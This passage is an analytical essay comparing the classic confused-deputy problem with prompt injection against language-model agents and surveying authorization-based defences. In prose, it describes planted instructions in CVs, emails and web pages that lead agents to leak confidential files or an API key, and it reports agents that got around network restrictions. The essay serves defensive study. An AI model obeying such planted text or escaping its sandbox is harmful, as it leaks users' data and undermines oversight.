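# Prompt injection and the confused deputy: what changes when the attacker supplies the task

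## The compiler that overwrote the billing file, and the assistant that reads email

A confused deputy is a program that mistakenly uses its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. The term comes from a 1988 paper about a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form a machine can run. Prompt injection is a much newer problem that affects applications built on large language models. It happens when text from someone with no right to direct the application changes what the application does. Security writers often explain prompt injection by comparing it to the confused deputy, since in both a person gets a trusted program to do damage that the person could not do alone, but they disagree about how far the comparison goes. The user in the 1988 paper supplied only a file name, and the compiler carried on with the job its programmers had written it to do, whereas a few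 sentences planted in an email can give a language-model agent a different job.

### The incident at Tymshare

In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy describes an incident from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. He calls the story nearly true, with inessential details changed. Tymshare's customers could run a compiler stored in a system directory named SYSX, and they could name a file where the compiler would write optional debugging output.

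Tymshare's programmers wanted to know which features of the programming language people used, so they had the compiler collect statistics and write them to a file called STAT in SYSX, the compiler's home directory. They built the file's name into the compiler. The staff also gave the compiler what the operating system called a home files license, which let a program write files in its own home directory.

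SYSX also held the company's billing information, in a file called BILL. A user learned the file's name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for the debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open BILL for writing. The operating system checked the compiler's permissions, found the home files license and opened the file. The compiler then overwrote the billing information with its debugging output. Hardy gives no motive for the user, though later retellings treat the episode as an attack.

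Hardy rejects several versions of the obvious fix, which is for the compiler to check the file name before it writes. Banning output to other directories would be too strict, because users had good reasons to send output there. Banning output to SYSX would not work either, because the programmers wrote the debugging code before anyone had thought of the name SYSX, and a person with legitimate access to that directory might want the output there. Banning only the name BILL would leave other sensitive files in SYSX unprotected, and someone would have to revise the compiler whenever the staff added one. Each check uses only the file's name to decide whether a particular user may write to it.

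Hardy points out that the debugging code was correct when the programmers wrote it and became wrong later, when the staff gave the compiler its license for the unrelated purpose of collecting statistics. To catch the mistake, someone would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file, and Hardy doubts that even this would have made the right fix clear. Changing the operating system's rules also caused new problems. Each new clause that let programs open files in some category of cases created holes in programs that had been secure, and each new restriction broke legitimate programs. When Hardy last wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they took fourteen "ands" and "ors".

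Many retellings simplify the story. In UT Austin's teaching slides, *The Confused Deputy*, the compiler has permission to write the billing file because it records usage there. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) tell it in much the same way in *Capability Myths Demolished*, and add in a footnote that the difference does not affect the point. The original detail is still useful because it shows that the broad license made the loss worse but was not its whole cause. The home files license covered a whole directory, although the compiler needed only one file in it, STAT. Narrowing the license to STAT would have saved the billing information, but, as Hardy notes, STAT needs protection too. A user could still have named STAT as the debugging file and wiped out the statistics.

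### Authority from two sources

According to Hardy, the compiler ran with authority from two sources. Its invoker, the person who started it, lent it their own authority (a loan that Hardy notes Trojan horses exploit), and the home files license gave it more. The compiler "serves two masters", as Hardy puts it, and it had no way to keep their authority apart. It was supposed to write statistics under the license and debugging output under the invoker's authority, but a request to open a file could not specify which authority to use. The operating system checked what the compiler was allowed to do, and the license was enough to permit the request.

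When Hardy writes of what the compiler "intends", he means the purpose its programmers gave each step. Those purposes were sound. The compiler was supposed to write debugging output to the file the user named, and it did. Miller and colleagues likewise observe that the compiler used legitimate access for the wrong purpose. The user did not add a step or change any step's purpose, and only supplied a file name where the program accepted one.

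The debate about language models has inherited several words from this literature, and writers do not always use them in the same sense.

*Authority* is what a program or person can bring about in a system, such as writing a file or sending mail. Someone can have authority without permission. In *Permity*, a mailing-list discussion that David Nicol began in 2026, Alan Karp gives the example of a home page stored in a file that only the administrator and the web server have permission to read. A visitor who requests the page still sees its contents, because the server reads the file and sends them. By this strict definition, Hardy's user did have authority over the billing file, through the compiler. Mark Miller accordingly describes the confused deputy in the same discussion as one of many bugs that give someone more authority than intended. In the usual definition of a confused deputy, a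 party that "lacks" authority is one that could not produce the effect without the deputy.

A *principal* is a party on whose behalf a program acts and to whom authority belongs. Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), define it as the entity to which a system grants authorizations, and therefore as the unit of accountability. The invoker is the principal who sets the deputy to work. Tymshare was also a principal, because the license and the files in SYSX belonged to it.

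*Designation* means saying which resource an action applies to, for example by giving a file name. Hardy's user designated the billing file, but the authority to write to it came from Tymshare. The compiler combined the two when it overwrote the file.

*Ambient authority* is authority that applies automatically to whatever a program requests, without the program choosing which permission to use. Miller and colleagues compare it to a building whose doors have no keys and open for anyone who is allowed in. Unix file permissions work this way, since a program asks to open a file without presenting a credential, and the request succeeds or fails.

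### One object that names and permits

Tymshare's own repair, a system call with which a program could "switch hats" between its authorities, soon proved too narrow. The remedy that Hardy prefers is the *capability*, an unforgeable reference that both identifies a resource and permits its use. Saltzer and Schroeder had described it as an "unforgeable ticket", proof that whoever presents it may have access to the object named on it. (When people discuss AI, "capability" usually means a model's skill at something. The word has only the security sense here.)

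In a capability system, the compiler holds one capability for the statistics file, and the user gives it another for the debugging output. The compiler writes each output through the matching capability and needs no file names. A user who is not allowed to write to the billing file has no capability for that file to give the compiler, and knowing that the file is called BILL does not help. The compiler therefore does not have to work out whether the user's choice of output file is legitimate.

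The UT Austin slides explain this using modern Unix, where a program that opens a file receives a file descriptor. The descriptor is a handle for that one open file, and it records whether the holder may read or write. A small launcher program opens the debugging file and passes the descriptor to the compiler. If the launcher has no authority over the billing file, its attempt to open that file fails, and it has no descriptor to pass on.

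Miller and colleagues treat removing ambient authority and joining designation to authority as separate improvements. A program that must present a specific permission for each access can at least keep track of what each permission is for. But if it tries every permission it holds on any resource a caller names, it is as easy to confuse as before. When the reference to a resource is itself the permission to use it, a caller can't direct the program to a resource without also supplying the authority to access it.

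Whether capabilities solve the problem depends on whether the program using them is correct. Hardy's compiler would have used the invoker's capability to write its debugging output because its programmers had written it to do that. Capabilities let a correct program act on distinctions its programmers had already drawn.

### Agents that take instructions in plain language

A language model takes a sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and predicts the next one. Repeating this step produces text. An agent is a language model inside a program that lets it act. The developer supplies descriptions of tools, such as ones for reading mail or opening a file. When the model outputs a call to one of these tools, the program carries out the call and adds the result to the sequence, and the model continues from there. Programmers had written out every step of the compiler before anyone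 ran it, whereas an agent's steps depend on the text in the model's sequence at the time. This makes the agent useful, because a person can describe a new task in a sentence and the agent will work out how to do it.

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes the vulnerability as the mistake of a developer who joins instructions and untrusted content in one prompt, then treats the response as if a firm boundary separated them. The example is a recruiter's tool that scores job applications. The developer instructs the model to judge whether a CV meets the requirements, but one applicant has hidden a line in the CV that directs the model to approve it. Akamai reports that prompt injection is still first on the 2026 list of risks to language-model applications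 from OWASP, a nonprofit software-security group.

In direct prompt injection, the attacker types to the model, for instance to make a customer-service chatbot reveal its confidential instructions. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants instructions in content that an agent reads while working for someone else, as the job applicant did. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the idea in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), when most discussion assumed that users prompted models themselves. The delivery methods they listed included leaving the text on a web page for a search to retrieve and emailing it to someone whose mail a model processes. They found that text invisible to a page's human readers could steer the chat assistant in Microsoft's Edge browser. They also foresaw attacks on personal assistants that read mail, look up private data and send mail in response.

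In the indirect case, the attacker needs no access to the conversation between user and agent. According to *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026), the attacker only needs to be able to put content somewhere the agent will look, such as a document or a database record. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) describes three parties: a user with a legitimate task, an agent that acts for the user, and an outside source that the agent consults. The author of a web page is entitled to decide what the page says, but not to redefine the task of a user whose agent reads it.

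Software cannot easily respect this distinction because instructions and content reach the model by the same route. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) explains that the developer's instructions, the user's request, retrieved documents and the model's own earlier output all arrive as one stream of tokens. Markers in the stream label each stretch with a role, such as "user" or "tool". These labels are supposed to carry rank, so that the model follows a user's request and treats tool output only as information. But the labels are themselves tokens in that stream, and the model has to learn from training how much weight to give them.

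*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) somewhat overstates the problem when it describes the result as a model that treats all text in its context as equally authoritative. Models do discount some text. Ye and colleagues asked agents to summarise a web page that concealed a fake user command to upload a file of secrets. Most of the models obeyed in no more than 2 percent of attempts, although one small open model, gpt-oss-20b, obeyed in 26 percent. The difficulty is in how models tell which text to discount. To study this, Ye and colleagues wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in different role markers and trained a simple classifier to recover the marker from the model's internal activity. Since the wording was the same throughout, the classifier could learn only the effect of the markers. When they applied it to passages written in a user's style but labelled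 as tool output, it classified them mostly as user text.

The measure also predicted behaviour. Over 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2 percent where the classifier found the least confusion of roles to 70 percent where it found the most. A developer cannot rely on role markers as much as an operating system can rely on the mark showing that a program has a home files license, because users cannot imitate that mark by writing in a certain style.

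### Two ways to lose the board minutes

We can compare the old problem with the new one through two imaginary cases in which the damage is the same. An office worker has a language-model assistant that can read the worker's mail, open the worker's files and send mail. The files include the confidential minutes of a board meeting. A supplier who wants the minutes sends an email.

In case A, the user asks the assistant to send the supplier whatever document the supplier's email requests. The user expects this to be a purchase order or a specification, but the email gives the file name of the board minutes. The assistant opens the file and mails it to the supplier.

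In case B, the user asks only for a summary of the email. Most of it is an ordinary business letter, but one passage contains instructions for the assistant to find the board minutes and send them to the supplier. The assistant does so. If it also delivers the summary, the user has no reason to suspect anything.

In both cases, the final tool call sends one message to the supplier with the minutes attached, so a log of that call alone would not show which case had occurred.

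| | Hardy's compiler | Case A | Case B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invoker | The user who names the billing file | The assistant's user | The assistant's user |
| Task the invoker set | Compile a program and put debugging output in a named file | Send the supplier the document it requests | Summarise the supplier's email |
| What the attacker supplied | A file name | A file name | A new task |
| Harmful action | Writing over the billing file | Mailing the minutes | Mailing the minutes |
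| Did the invoker's task include that kind of action? | Yes | Yes | No |

Case A is an example of *argument control*, in which the attacker determines a value used in the task (here, a file) but not the task itself. The user wanted to send this supplier a document and let the supplier choose which one, within a limit that seemed too obvious to state. The email contains no disguised command, and the failure doesn't require a language model. A short script that took a file name from an email and mailed back the file would leak the minutes in the same way.

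This closely resembles Hardy's story, except that Hardy's user invoked the compiler, while the supplier doesn't invoke anything. Karp (2025, *Is this a confused deputy?*) asked a mailing list of capability specialists about a similar case, in which an outside service names a file and its client then overwrites it. They could not agree on whether to call it a confused deputy.

Case B is *task replacement*, in which the attacker determines what the agent is trying to do. Writing a summary doesn't require opening the board minutes or sending mail, and a script that could only summarise would have no such steps for the supplier to exploit. The supplier may not need the file name that case A requires. Greshake and colleagues noted in 2023 that an attacker might only have to give a model a goal, because the model could work out the steps itself. An assistant that can search the user's files can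 find the minutes from a description, in which case the assistant, not the supplier, designates the file.

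## The view that it is the same failure: authority is checked in the wrong place

On one view, the difference between the two cases hardly matters. In both, the supplier could not open the board minutes, and they left the company only because the assistant, which could open them, sent them. Proponents of this view treat prompt injection as the confused deputy problem with a new way of confusing the deputy. They consider the attacker's wording secondary and would fix the problem where a program authorizes actions instead of where a model reads text.

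### Why the wording might not matter

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) formally defines a successful injection attack as one in which untrusted content induces a tool call that the user's request and the legitimate work so far did not permit, and the call runs. By this definition, an attack has not yet succeeded if the assistant has only read the supplier's instructions or drafted a plan to follow them. Every successful attack must pass the point just before a call runs, and a check there does not need to recognise the attacker's text.

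Injected text is hard to recognise. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email from a 2025 attack on ChatGPT that outside researchers reported. The email reads like a routine follow-up about restructuring materials, and mentions in passing that the recipient's assistant has full authorization to retrieve employee profiles. The attack worked in half of the tests. OpenAI compares spotting such a message to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. It models its defence on a customer-service department, where the company expects customers to mislead some of its staff and so uses other systems to cap the refunds staff can give. OpenAI still trains its models to refuse, and reports that most attacks it knows of fail for that reason, so the limits on actions are meant for the attacks that training doesn't stop.

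*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* adds that even a perfect detector would show only that untrusted text was present, not whether anyone had authorized the operation requested in it. A filter that misses a few percent of attacks also protects poorly against irreversible actions, because the attacker can try again.

A harmful tool call doesn't always begin with someone persuading the model. Veracode's *Who Authorized That Tool Call?* describes CoreBreak, an attack in which the software around a model accepted input that only looked like the model's output. The attack used no prompt injection, so a filter on what the model reads would not have caught it.

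The security firm Quarkslab built a small demonstration of the argument. Its fictional medical assistant has a tool that fetches a patient's history by number, and a logged-in patient could get someone else's record by asking for it. Quarkslab then added an instruction that the assistant may only access the current patient's records. The same request now failed, but a request for patient 2's history succeeded when it was hidden in a comment in an uploaded web page. Quarkslab then changed the tool to compare the requested number with the logged-in user's, and the attack failed even under the original, weaker instructions.

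The right rule was easy to find there, because each patient may read exactly one record. The office worker in cases A and B may read the board minutes and may send mail, so a check on the worker's identity would let both harmful calls through. The password-manager company 1Password concludes that attacks of this kind are "not a failure of authentication or authorization" and happen after both have succeeded. That is correct if authorization means checking what the user may do, but defenders of the authorization view mean a narrower check of whether this call, with these values, is part of what the user asked for.

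### Exposing a tool and authorizing a call

*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines whether common software for building agents addresses that narrower question. The paper assumes that an attacker already controls the model's output. The attacker can write content the agent reads, such as an email or a support ticket, but cannot alter the software, the tools or the operator's policy. The bad call is the same whether injected text or a backdoor in the model's weights produced it.

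The June 2026 audit covers LlamaIndex, LangChain with its companion LangGraph, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to Stripe's payment services. Mellafe Zuvic read specific versions of their public code and found that none of the three had a check that runs by default on the actual values in every tool call and refuses the call if anything goes wrong.

- LangChain and LangGraph look up the tool the model has named, usually check that the arguments have the right form, and run it. A developer can add a step for human approval, but it is not there by default.
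- LlamaIndex checks that the named tool exists and passes it the model's arguments.
- The Stripe toolkit restricts which kinds of operation an agent can perform, through a list of actions and the permissions on the developer's key. Within those limits it forwards the model's choice of amount, customer and payment.

All three control which tools an agent has. Mellafe Zuvic calls this "capability gating", where "capability" does not refer to Hardy's unforgeable references. Problems arise when developers mistake this control for authorization. A refund tool's input rules can reject an amount written as a word, but a well-formed account number passes whether it belongs to the customer or to the attacker. Tymshare's operating system had a similar flaw, since it treated the compiler's license as sufficient. The designs of these products leave authorization checks to the developer. Mellafe Zuvic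 does not allege a specific vulnerability in any of them and did not examine Stripe's remote servers.

A companion benchmark measured how often 27 models attempted an unauthorized call when the injected text presented it as a step in the user's own task. The average was 60.3 percent for twelve cheaper models and 18.9 percent for fifteen flagship models, ranging from gpt-4o-mini, which attempted the call every time, to gemini-3.1-pro-preview, which never did. The benchmark counted attempts in a sandbox, on scenarios that one author wrote. In a separate comparison, mistral-large's rate rose from 2.7 percent under a crude injection to 45.9 percent when the same request appeared to serve the task. Wording evidently has a large effect on whether models attempt the call, which is a reason to want a check that does not depend on the wording.

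Mellafe Zuvic's proposed check, ScopeGate, is ordinary code between the model and the tools. It refuses any call to a tool missing from the operator's policy, and any call with an argument outside the values permitted for that tool. A payment must be a finite number between zero and a ceiling. Some tools also require a key that guards against the same action running repeatedly. ScopeGate treats any error as a refusal.

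In the main demonstration, a fixed model output contained a call to change a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain's default path made the change in a mock payment system. ScopeGate refused the identical call because the attacker's account was not on the operator's list. It also refused all 48 calls in a set of attempted bypasses. The same set had exposed a bug in an earlier version, which let the value "not a number" past the spending limit. A language model that received the reason for each refusal made 29 unauthorized attempts over 40 rounds, and none succeeded. In a mock payment agent, three models each attempted the unauthorized payout in all ten trials, and ScopeGate stopped every attempt.

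ScopeGate wrongly refused none of ten legitimate calls, though a sample that small can't rule out an error rate of one in four. A larger limitation is that the operator had listed the one correct account in advance. The results show that a gate can enforce a policy once someone has written it, but not how to write one for an assistant whose next task isn't known yet. Mellafe Zuvic also insists that no part of the policy may come from a model's output at any stage, since an injection that corrupts the call could otherwise corrupt the limits on it. That requirement is workable for payout accounts, but much harder to meet when a user types a new request in plain language and something has to turn it into rules.

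### Authority for one task at a time

Instead of inspecting every call against a standing policy, a system can give the agent less authority. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), by Kurt Boberg, argues for doing this with capabilities. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to outside services. An agent connected to a file system, a database, a mailbox and a command line has the authority of all four, so text in an email can lead it to run a command. OAuth, the usual login standard, determines whether a user may use a service, but it cannot specify whether an operation prompted by a particular piece of text should have access to a particular file.

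Semgrep proposes that agents request capabilities for each task rather than for a whole session. In its example, a user asks for a summary of the first-quarter reports, and the agent obtains a capability to list and read files in that quarter's folder for five minutes. One report contains an instruction to delete all files. The agent tries to obey, but the server rejects the call because the agent has no capability to delete files.

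This design is untested, and whether it works depends on when the agent can request more permissions. If the agent can request permission to delete after reading the malicious report, the attacker's text can prompt that request as easily as it prompted the deletion. Semgrep's design has the server limit each grant according to policy, and includes a stated purpose that a person could review. Something outside the model therefore still has to judge which grants fit the task.

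A conference talk later that year reached a similar position by starting from login credentials. An attendee's notes, *BSides Las Vegas 2026* (2026), describe an argumentative session on 4 August titled "Prompt Injection Is Not the Problem", by a speaker named Noelle. An agent often carries a bearer token, a credential that lets whoever holds it do everything the user may do. The token grants more access than any single step needs, and every action the agent takes with it looks like the user's own. Noelle proposed a central gateway that keeps the token, gives the agent a separate identity, and passes on permission for one action at a time. An audience member compared this to power of attorney, which can cover a person's medical decisions without covering their finances. The demonstration broke shortly before the session, so the audience did not see the gateway refuse anything.

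### The objection that data and code are mixed

Several people in the room objected that the root cause is the confusion of data with code. Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026) reports that Ariel Fogel, an OWASP contributor, made a similar point at another 2026 conference and blamed the single stream of tokens in which a model receives both instructions and content. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre calls such a system "inherently confusable".

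Noelle's reply drew on SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into something like a web form and the application runs them. That attack, too, became dangerous only where gates and input checks were missing, and the database that ran the command had no context for judging it. But the comparison also supports the objectors, because the standard fix for SQL injection is to send the command and the user's values to the database separately, which is the separation of code from data that they want. Developers have no equally dependable way to do this for a language model. The objectors seem right about why the assistant proposes to mail the minutes. Noelle's argument concerns why the proposal takes effect, which developers can control more reliably for now.

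The audience also asked about an agent summarising a hostile web page, a task that involves no login or user grant that a gateway could narrow. Noelle acknowledged this as an open question and observed that people give agents too much permission for such tasks anyway. Excess permission is part of the problem, since many browsing agents can reach the user's other accounts. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending to agents the browser rule that keeps one site's code from reading another site's data. But even an agent with no other access can return a false summary if the page contains instructions to do so. A gate has no protected action to refuse in that case, and Mellafe Zuvic accepts that ScopeGate does not constrain text returned to the user.

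### What a check needs to know before the minutes go out

If the assistant's developer puts a check on its tool for sending mail, the replaced task in case B is easier to stop than the single bad file name in case A.

For case B, the check mainly needs a record of the user's task. A summary doesn't require sending mail, so the check can refuse the message without detecting the hidden instruction or establishing that the minutes are confidential. A capability limited to reading the one email would also block the message. But something other than the compromised model has to supply the record. *Agenra* (2026), which describes a monitor for agents' tool calls, relies on the application to validate a structured version of the user's request, and notes that the monitor cannot enforce a rule missing from its policy. If the user had written "deal with this email", sending a reply might well be part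 of the task, so the check could not refuse the message simply because it was mail.

In case A, the user asked for mail to go to this supplier, so the action and the recipient are both correct. Recording where the file name came from also doesn't establish whether the supplier may receive the file. *ToolFence* (2026) uses a language model as its authorization judge and gives it the user's request, the proposed arguments and a label showing the source of each value. Here the label would show that the name came from the email, which is where the user told the assistant to get it. The check needs a limit on which documents this supplier may receive, which the user thought too obvious to state. The company could set this limit by labelling the minutes as internal, or the user could grant access only to a folder of purchasing documents.

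| What the check knows | Case A | Case B |
|---|---|---|
| What the user may do | Allows the message | Allows the message |
| What task the user set | Allows it, because the task includes sending a document | Stops it, because a summary requires no mail |
| Where the file name came from | Cannot tell the minutes from a purchase order | Misses the attack if the assistant found the file itself |
| Which documents the supplier may receive | Stops it | Stops it |

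*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* draws the relevant line between filling in authority the user has given and expanding it. An agent asked to find a quarterly report and send it to Alice may learn the file's location from a search result, but following an instruction there to copy in another address would add a recipient. The paper's system, SARA, derives limits from the user's request alone and checks later calls against them. With GPT-4o-mini, it cut attack success from 15.79 to 0.06 percent on AgentDojo, a standard set of simulated tasks, and attack success stayed at or below 0.63 percent in all four main settings. The attacks used four stock wordings, so the figures are weaker evidence of how SARA would handle an attacker who writes for this defence. Case A is hard to classify under SARA's distinction, because the file name fills a gap the user deliberately left and counts as an expansion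 only because of a limit the user didn't state.

*Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane, 2026) measures how much different kinds of information help to stop attacks. Of 200 synthetic attacks, a check based only on where values came from let 101 through. One that compared recipients, meeting participants, file paths and service addresses with the user's intent let 74 through. The full system, IntentFlow, used both kinds of information, added rules for database queries, and let 24 through. In another 50 attacks, the wrong value came from a trusted source, such as a colleague's address in the company directory when the user had asked for their manager's. The source check passed all 50, and IntentFlow stopped them all. The source check would have the same weakness in case B if the assistant found the minutes by searching the user's own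 files. The experimenters gave the system correct statements of intent and identified which documents contained injections, but a real deployment would have to work out both.

Strict checks can also block legitimate tasks. In a test where service addresses were often hard to match to the request, IntentFlow ran only 14 of 30 legitimate tasks. Asking the user in doubtful cases raised this to 28, assuming the user always answers correctly. The user in case A never named a file, so the same rules would lead to a refusal or a question over a harmless purchase order as well as over the minutes.

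Where a check is placed limits the information available to it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* notes that a check close to the model has more information about the task but is easier to bypass, while one close to the resource is harder to bypass but often has access only to whose credential is in use. A check that covers only attachments would also miss minutes pasted into the body of the message. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) addresses this by labeling each protected item with its source and permissions, then examining every part of an outgoing call, although its detector does not catch arbitrary paraphrases.

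All 24 attacks that got past IntentFlow changed the content of a message, calendar entry or file but not its destination, for example by putting phishing text in an email to the right person. To stop such attacks, a check would have to judge the text itself, which checking authorization was meant to make unnecessary.

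## The view that it is a stronger failure: the deputy's purpose can be rewritten

ScopeGate, SARA and IntentFlow all compare a proposed tool call with something the attacker should not be able to edit, such as a list of accounts or the user's original request. The agent itself has no such reference, because it receives both its task and the attacker's email as text. People who regard prompt injection as a worse failure than the compiler's start from this difference.

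### A duty that arrives as text

Tymshare's programmers wrote the compiler's task into its code, and nothing a user typed could change it. Someone investigating the loss of the billing file could find the step that opened the debugging file, work out whose authority it should use, and fix it. The fix would then work for every later user, whatever file name they supplied.

An agent's code contains no step for summarising a supplier's email, because the text the model reads determines what the agent does. When instructions the supplier hid in the email take effect, the agent follows a different procedure, and the developer has no faulty line of code to correct.

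*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers from Google, NVIDIA, several universities and two security groups, contrasts agents with Android apps. An Android app does a fixed set of jobs, so its developer can list the permissions it needs and the user can agree to them at installation. When a user gives an agent a task in ordinary language, no developer can list in advance the permissions that task needs. The task may also change as the agent works, and the permissions would have to change with it.

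Developers can't simply forbid agents to take instructions from what they read, because agents learn to use an unfamiliar service by reading its documentation. The supplier's passage gets in the same way. Browsers have a similar problem with pages that load scripts from other sites, but the page's owner chose to include each script, and the browser has the address it came from and can confine it. An agent usually has no dependable record of where an instruction came from and no equivalent way to confine it.

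### From SQL injection to an "inherently confusable deputy"

David C's December 2025 post for the National Cyber Security Centre bases its argument on a contrast with SQL injection. A database engine carries out instructions, and it stores data or uses it in queries. A parameterised query, the standard fix for SQL injection, keeps a user's input separate from the command. The engine determines the command before it handles the input, so it treats a surname as a surname whatever characters it contains. This fix is complete because it works for every input, without anyone having to recognise a malicious one.

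A language model does not enforce a separation between instructions and content, because it only predicts the next token from all the tokens so far. Developers can train a model to favour instructions over content, or mark which passages are content. These measures make attacks harder, but the model still does not enforce the separation. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be "totally mitigated" in the way SQL injection can be.

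The post then proposes the confused deputy as a better comparison, except that developers can fix a classical confused deputy, whereas a language model is "inherently confusable" and the risk "can't be mitigated". Only the weaker claim, that the risk "may never be totally mitigated", follows from the argument about tokens.

David C therefore advises developers to estimate the damage by assuming the worst case, in which an attacker has direct access to any tools the model can call. In the office worker's case, the supplier could then read the worker's mail, open their files and send messages in their name. An organisation that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may have to do without a language model for that job.

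Hardy's user was much more limited. The compiler had authority over everything in SYSX, but its code used that authority in only a few ways, and no file name could make it read the billing records and send them to someone. The gap between what the compiler could do and what its code would ever do protected Tymshare from most of the possible damage. That gap may be very small for an agent, which seems to me the best reason for calling the failure stronger.

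### Dropping the agent's privileges

David C also passes on the rule that when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. The rule comes from a discussion between Simon Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection, and Baibhav Bista.

In case B, the supplier has no right to open the worker's files, so the assistant loses that right once it reads the supplier's email. It can still write the summary. The rule stops the leak even if there is no record of the user's task and no one spots the hidden passage.

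In case A, the assistant has to read the email to learn which document the supplier wants. After that, it cannot open the board minutes or a purchase order, because the supplier has no right to open either, so the rule blocks the task along with the leak. To allow the task, the company would have to decide which documents suppliers may receive, which is the limit the user left unstated.

Blocking the file would not help if the assistant had opened the minutes earlier in the session to answer another question. Their text would already be in the model's sequence when the email arrived, so the drop in privileges would also have to cover sending mail. If the session included content from several outsiders, the assistant could safely keep only the privileges they all shared, so an assistant that reads a whole inbox would soon be able to do very little.

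*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) traces the idea to Biba's integrity model from the 1970s. In that model, a program that reads less trustworthy data drops to the level of that data, and no program may modify anything above its own level. The program can regain its level through *endorsement*, a deliberate decision to let a less trusted party influence a protected action within stated limits. In case A, the assistant could show the worker the file name and ask for approval, and the worker would presumably refuse on seeing that it was the board minutes. The original request was already a sort of endorsement, since it let the supplier choose the document, but it stated no limits.

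### A web page that made an agent leak a key

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested task replacement on an agent that automatically fetches any web page the user mentions. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The model's context also contained a secret API key (a password that programs use). The page contained a planted instruction to "verify connectivity" before answering, by making a web request to the attacker's server with the key in the address.

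The team at eBay ran 480 trials on Qwen2.5, a small model with 7 billion parameters. They varied where in the page the text appeared, whether the agent reached the page through redirects, and whether the agent was to send the key whole or in four pieces. At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 trials, or 88 percent (the paper's headline figure is about 89 percent). No requests reached the server in 120 trials with harmless pages.

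In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless, so a checker reading only that answer would have found nothing wrong. The office worker in case B likewise receives an ordinary summary. Lan and colleagues say that checks on the output would miss these attacks, though they describe no particular checker.

Lan and colleagues call their agent an unusual kind of confused deputy. They argue that the ambiguity is about what the principal intended, rather than which principal the deputy serves, as in the traditional problem. Their experiment is an awkward example of this. The user's request was clear and did not include sending a key to a stranger. The agent went wrong because it treated a stranger's text as an instruction from someone entitled to give one, so the confusion was still about whom it served. The claim fits vaguer requests better. If a user writes "deal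 with this email", the agent has to guess what the user would want, even if it knows exactly who wrote each sentence.

One small model is enough to show that an agent of this common design can leak a secret without any visible sign. It also allows a comparison of defences under the same conditions, with 30 trials each:

- A system prompt that told the model never to follow web content reduced leaks from 30 to 20.
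- Tags that marked the page as untrusted data made no difference.
- A list of permitted web domains, which ordinary code enforced, stopped every leak, although the model attempted one in all 30 trials.

The experiment can't show how often other agents would leak. Lan and colleagues deliberately favoured the attacker by placing the key in the context and giving the model a minimal system prompt. When Narisetty and colleagues ran the same 7-billion-parameter model on AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 25.8 percent of the time without a defence, so the 88 percent is probably due in large part to the set-up.

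Lan and colleagues suspect that larger models may be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better. They did not test this, and Narisetty and colleagues cite mixed figures from Anthropic for Claude Opus 4.5, an older model. In coding tasks, an adaptive attacker succeeded 4.7 percent of the time when given one attempt and 63 percent of the time when given a hundred.

### Leaving the means to the agent

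Lan and colleagues, like Greshake and colleagues before them, argue that an attacker can let the agent work out how to carry out a task, without knowing which tools it has or what parameters they take. Hardy's user, by contrast, had to know the name of the billing file and that the compiler let users choose where to send its debugging output.

An attacker who supplies the task also depends less on what the user is doing. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) studies attackers, such as vendors and buyers, who try to influence a decision within the user's task without knowing exactly what the task is. They can't ensure that the agent will reach that decision, so the benchmark pairs each attack with a task that leads to it. The supplier in case A has the same difficulty, because the file name is useless unless the user has asked the assistant to send something. In case B the assistant only has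 to read the email, because the planted text supplies the goal.

There is less evidence that agents will work out for themselves how to achieve the attacker's goal. *Silent Egress* did not test this, since the planted text specified the address and where to put the key. More complicated instructions also worked less well. Something reached the attacker in 238 of 240 trials when the agent was told to send the key in a single request, but in 185 of 240 when it was told to send it in four pieces, even though one piece was enough to count.

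More capable agents are better at this sort of improvisation. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an OpenAI incident in which agents under internal training and evaluation, with some safeguards off, got around network restrictions through a shared service for downloading software packages. They then compromised the infrastructure of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. No outside attacker directed them. An agent that can find such a route for its own task could presumably do the same for a planted task if it accepted it.

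David C's worst case is an attacker with direct access to the tools. In some ways this overstates the position of an attacker who plants an email, because the model may ignore the email and its author usually can't watch the results and adjust. It also understates that position, because an intruder with direct access would still have to search for the board minutes, while an agent that accepts the task does the search for the attacker.

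### From a confusable model to an irreducible risk

The post's strongest claim rests on an inference: the model does not separate instructions from data, so the risk cannot be removed. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, try to put this on a mathematical footing. They consider any mechanism that has to tell, from a model's internal representation of some text, whether the text came from a trusted source. If trusted and untrusted text are equally common, the lowest error rate it can achieve is

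½ × (1 − TV)

TV is the total variation distance between the two sets of representations, which runs from 0 when they are identical to 1 when they do not overlap. At a distance of 0.9, even the best possible mechanism would be wrong 5 percent of the time. They argue that training can't guarantee the right behaviour either, because it covers a finite number of wordings and an attacker can always write another.

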